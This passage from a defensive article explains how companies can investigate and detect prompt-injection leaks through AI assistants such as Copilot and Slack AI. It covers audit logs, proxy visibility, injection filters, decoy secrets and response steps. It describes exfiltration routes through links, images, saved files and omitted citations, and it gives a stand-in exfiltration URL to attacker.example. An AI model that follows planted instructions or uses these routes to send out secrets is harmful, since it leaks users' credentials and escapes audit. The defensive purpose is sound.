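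Customers paste secrets into support requests, much as employees paste them into Slack. Cloudflare, one of the affected companies, searched the records stolen from it for secrets, as an attacker would. It found 104 of its API tokens and replaced them.

The thieves deleted some of their search jobs, but the underlying logs survived, so customers could see what the thieves had taken. A bulk copy through a connected program tends to leave a record of many unusual requests, while a leak through an assistant may consist of one ordinary question and one web request.

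### Which logs would contain the leak?

An investigator needs the employee's question, the items the assistant retrieved, and the request that carried the data out. These are usually in different places.

Microsoft's audit log records who used Copilot, when, in which program, and which files and emails it drew on. Microsoft stores the text of the question and answer separately, in the user's mailbox, where an authorised investigator can search it. Slack's audit entries may not list every retrieved message.

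A list of citations is a poor substitute for a list of retrieved items, because the model helps choose the citations and the attacker may control the model. Slack AI did not cite the planted message in the 2024 demonstration, and neither did Copilot in EchoLeak.

The audit log can have the same problem. In 2025, the security researcher Zack Korman found that the log could omit a file if a user asked Copilot to summarise it without linking to it. Microsoft fixed this in August 2025. Before then, an attacker who made Copilot leave out a citation might also have kept the file out of the log.

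Developers who build their own bots can avoid this by having the search software, not the model, record the identifier of every item it passes on. Identifiers are better than full text because logging the text would create another copy of each secret. Most retrieved items are harmless and uncited, so an investigator should start with those that came from outsiders or obscure channels.

The outgoing request is harder to find, because the company's equipment often doesn't send it. Many companies route employees' web traffic through a proxy, a server that logs it. The proxy's log is useful for some routes and useless for others:

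| Route | First request comes from | What the company's proxy can log |
|---|---|---|
| Clicked link | Employee's browser | The attacker's site |
| Image passed on by Teams or Bing | Employee's browser | A Microsoft site, with the attacker's address inside the request |
| Link preview in Slack | Slack's server | Nothing |
| Link in a file Copilot saved | Microsoft's server | Nothing |
| Code in Copilot's sandbox | Microsoft's server | Nothing |

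Even in the first two rows, the proxy records the full address only if the company decrypts its employees' traffic. Otherwise it logs only the host name, so all visits to Bing look the same. ThaiCERT advises administrators to look for abnormal connections to Bing's image services and for Copilot search links with unusual or encoded queries. The advice is reasonable, but a company first needs to know what its normal traffic looks like.

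Microsoft has published searches that find prompts inside links in emails and Teams messages, and inside links that employees clicked. The searches look for words such as "remember" and "trusted", which suit the advertising prompts. A link that tells Copilot to find a login code may contain none of these words, so a security team worried about theft would need to search for different ones.

### Catching the planted text on arrival

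Ideally, an organisation finds the planted message before an assistant reads it. In July 2026, Microsoft began previewing a feature that detects planted instructions in email, according to Microsoft's *MC1422060* (2026). The feature quarantines messages detected with high confidence and labels them "Prompt Injection" so administrators can search for them. Microsoft later moved the general release from September to October.

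The feature covers email but not messages posted in a Teams or Slack channel, and it is only included in the more expensive plans. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Defender for Office 365 Blocks Prompt Injections* (2026) points out that Copilot can also read shared mailboxes that its user has permission to open. A shared mailbox like `support@company.example` receives a lot of mail from strangers, so it needs the same protection as an employee's own mailbox.

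Searching for tag characters is simpler and should produce few false alarms after some adjustment. Microsoft's first version kept flagging the emoji for the flags of England, Scotland and Wales, which use those characters legitimately. But the search detects only one way of hiding instructions, and it would miss instructions written in ordinary visible English.

### Decoy secrets

A decoy secret can reveal a theft that left no clear trace in the assistant's logs. Security specialists call it a honeytoken or canary token. It works like this:

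1. The security team creates a key that looks real but gives access to nothing useful.
2. It puts the key in an old thread or document where a thief might find it.
3. The service that issued the key watches for attempts to use it.
4. Nobody has a legitimate reason to use the key, so any attempt raises an alarm, with the time and the network address it came from.

If each channel has a different decoy, the alarm also shows which channel leaked, but not how, since someone using a stolen Slack password would set off the same alarm.

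Decoys are much better at catching bulk theft than a single leak. Suppose a workspace contains 36 real secrets and four decoys. A thief who steals one at random and tries it has a 10% chance of picking a decoy. A thief who copies everything and tries ten at random has about a 70% chance of trying at least one decoy. An attacker who asked for a named key, as in the attack on Slack AI, would probably miss the decoys.

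To catch that attack, the decoy has to appear in the results for questions employees ask. But then employees will sometimes get the decoy too and set off a false alarm by trying to log in with it. A team could accept a few false alarms for its most valuable systems and hide its other decoys in threads that nobody normally needs.

### What should the company do first?

If an employee reports an odd answer containing a link to `attacker.example/report?c=DUMMY-KEY`, the company should first revoke the key, which takes minutes and can be done before anyone understands the attack. It should then revoke any other secrets in the assistant's context, including those from earlier in the conversation, because the visible link may not be the only way data got out.

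Next, the team should find the planted text, starting with the uncited items in the retrieval log. Searching for `attacker.example` may also work, unless the attacker disguised the address. Before deleting the message, the team should save a copy of it and its identifier, and look for the same text in other channels and mailboxes. If the planted text is immediately obvious, one person can hide it from the assistant while another revokes the key.

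Deleting the message may not be enough if the assistant keeps memories between conversations. Microsoft advises users to check their assistant's saved memories and remove any they don't recognise. The team should also look for files the assistant created, since one of the ReLeak attacks sent data through a saved document.

The last step is to search the logs for every other answer that used the planted text. Each one may have exposed a different employee's secrets, which the company has to revoke as well. If the logs don't list the items the assistant retrieved, the team has to identify everyone whose answers could have used the text. For a message in a public channel, that is everyone in the workspace who asked the assistant a question while the message was there.
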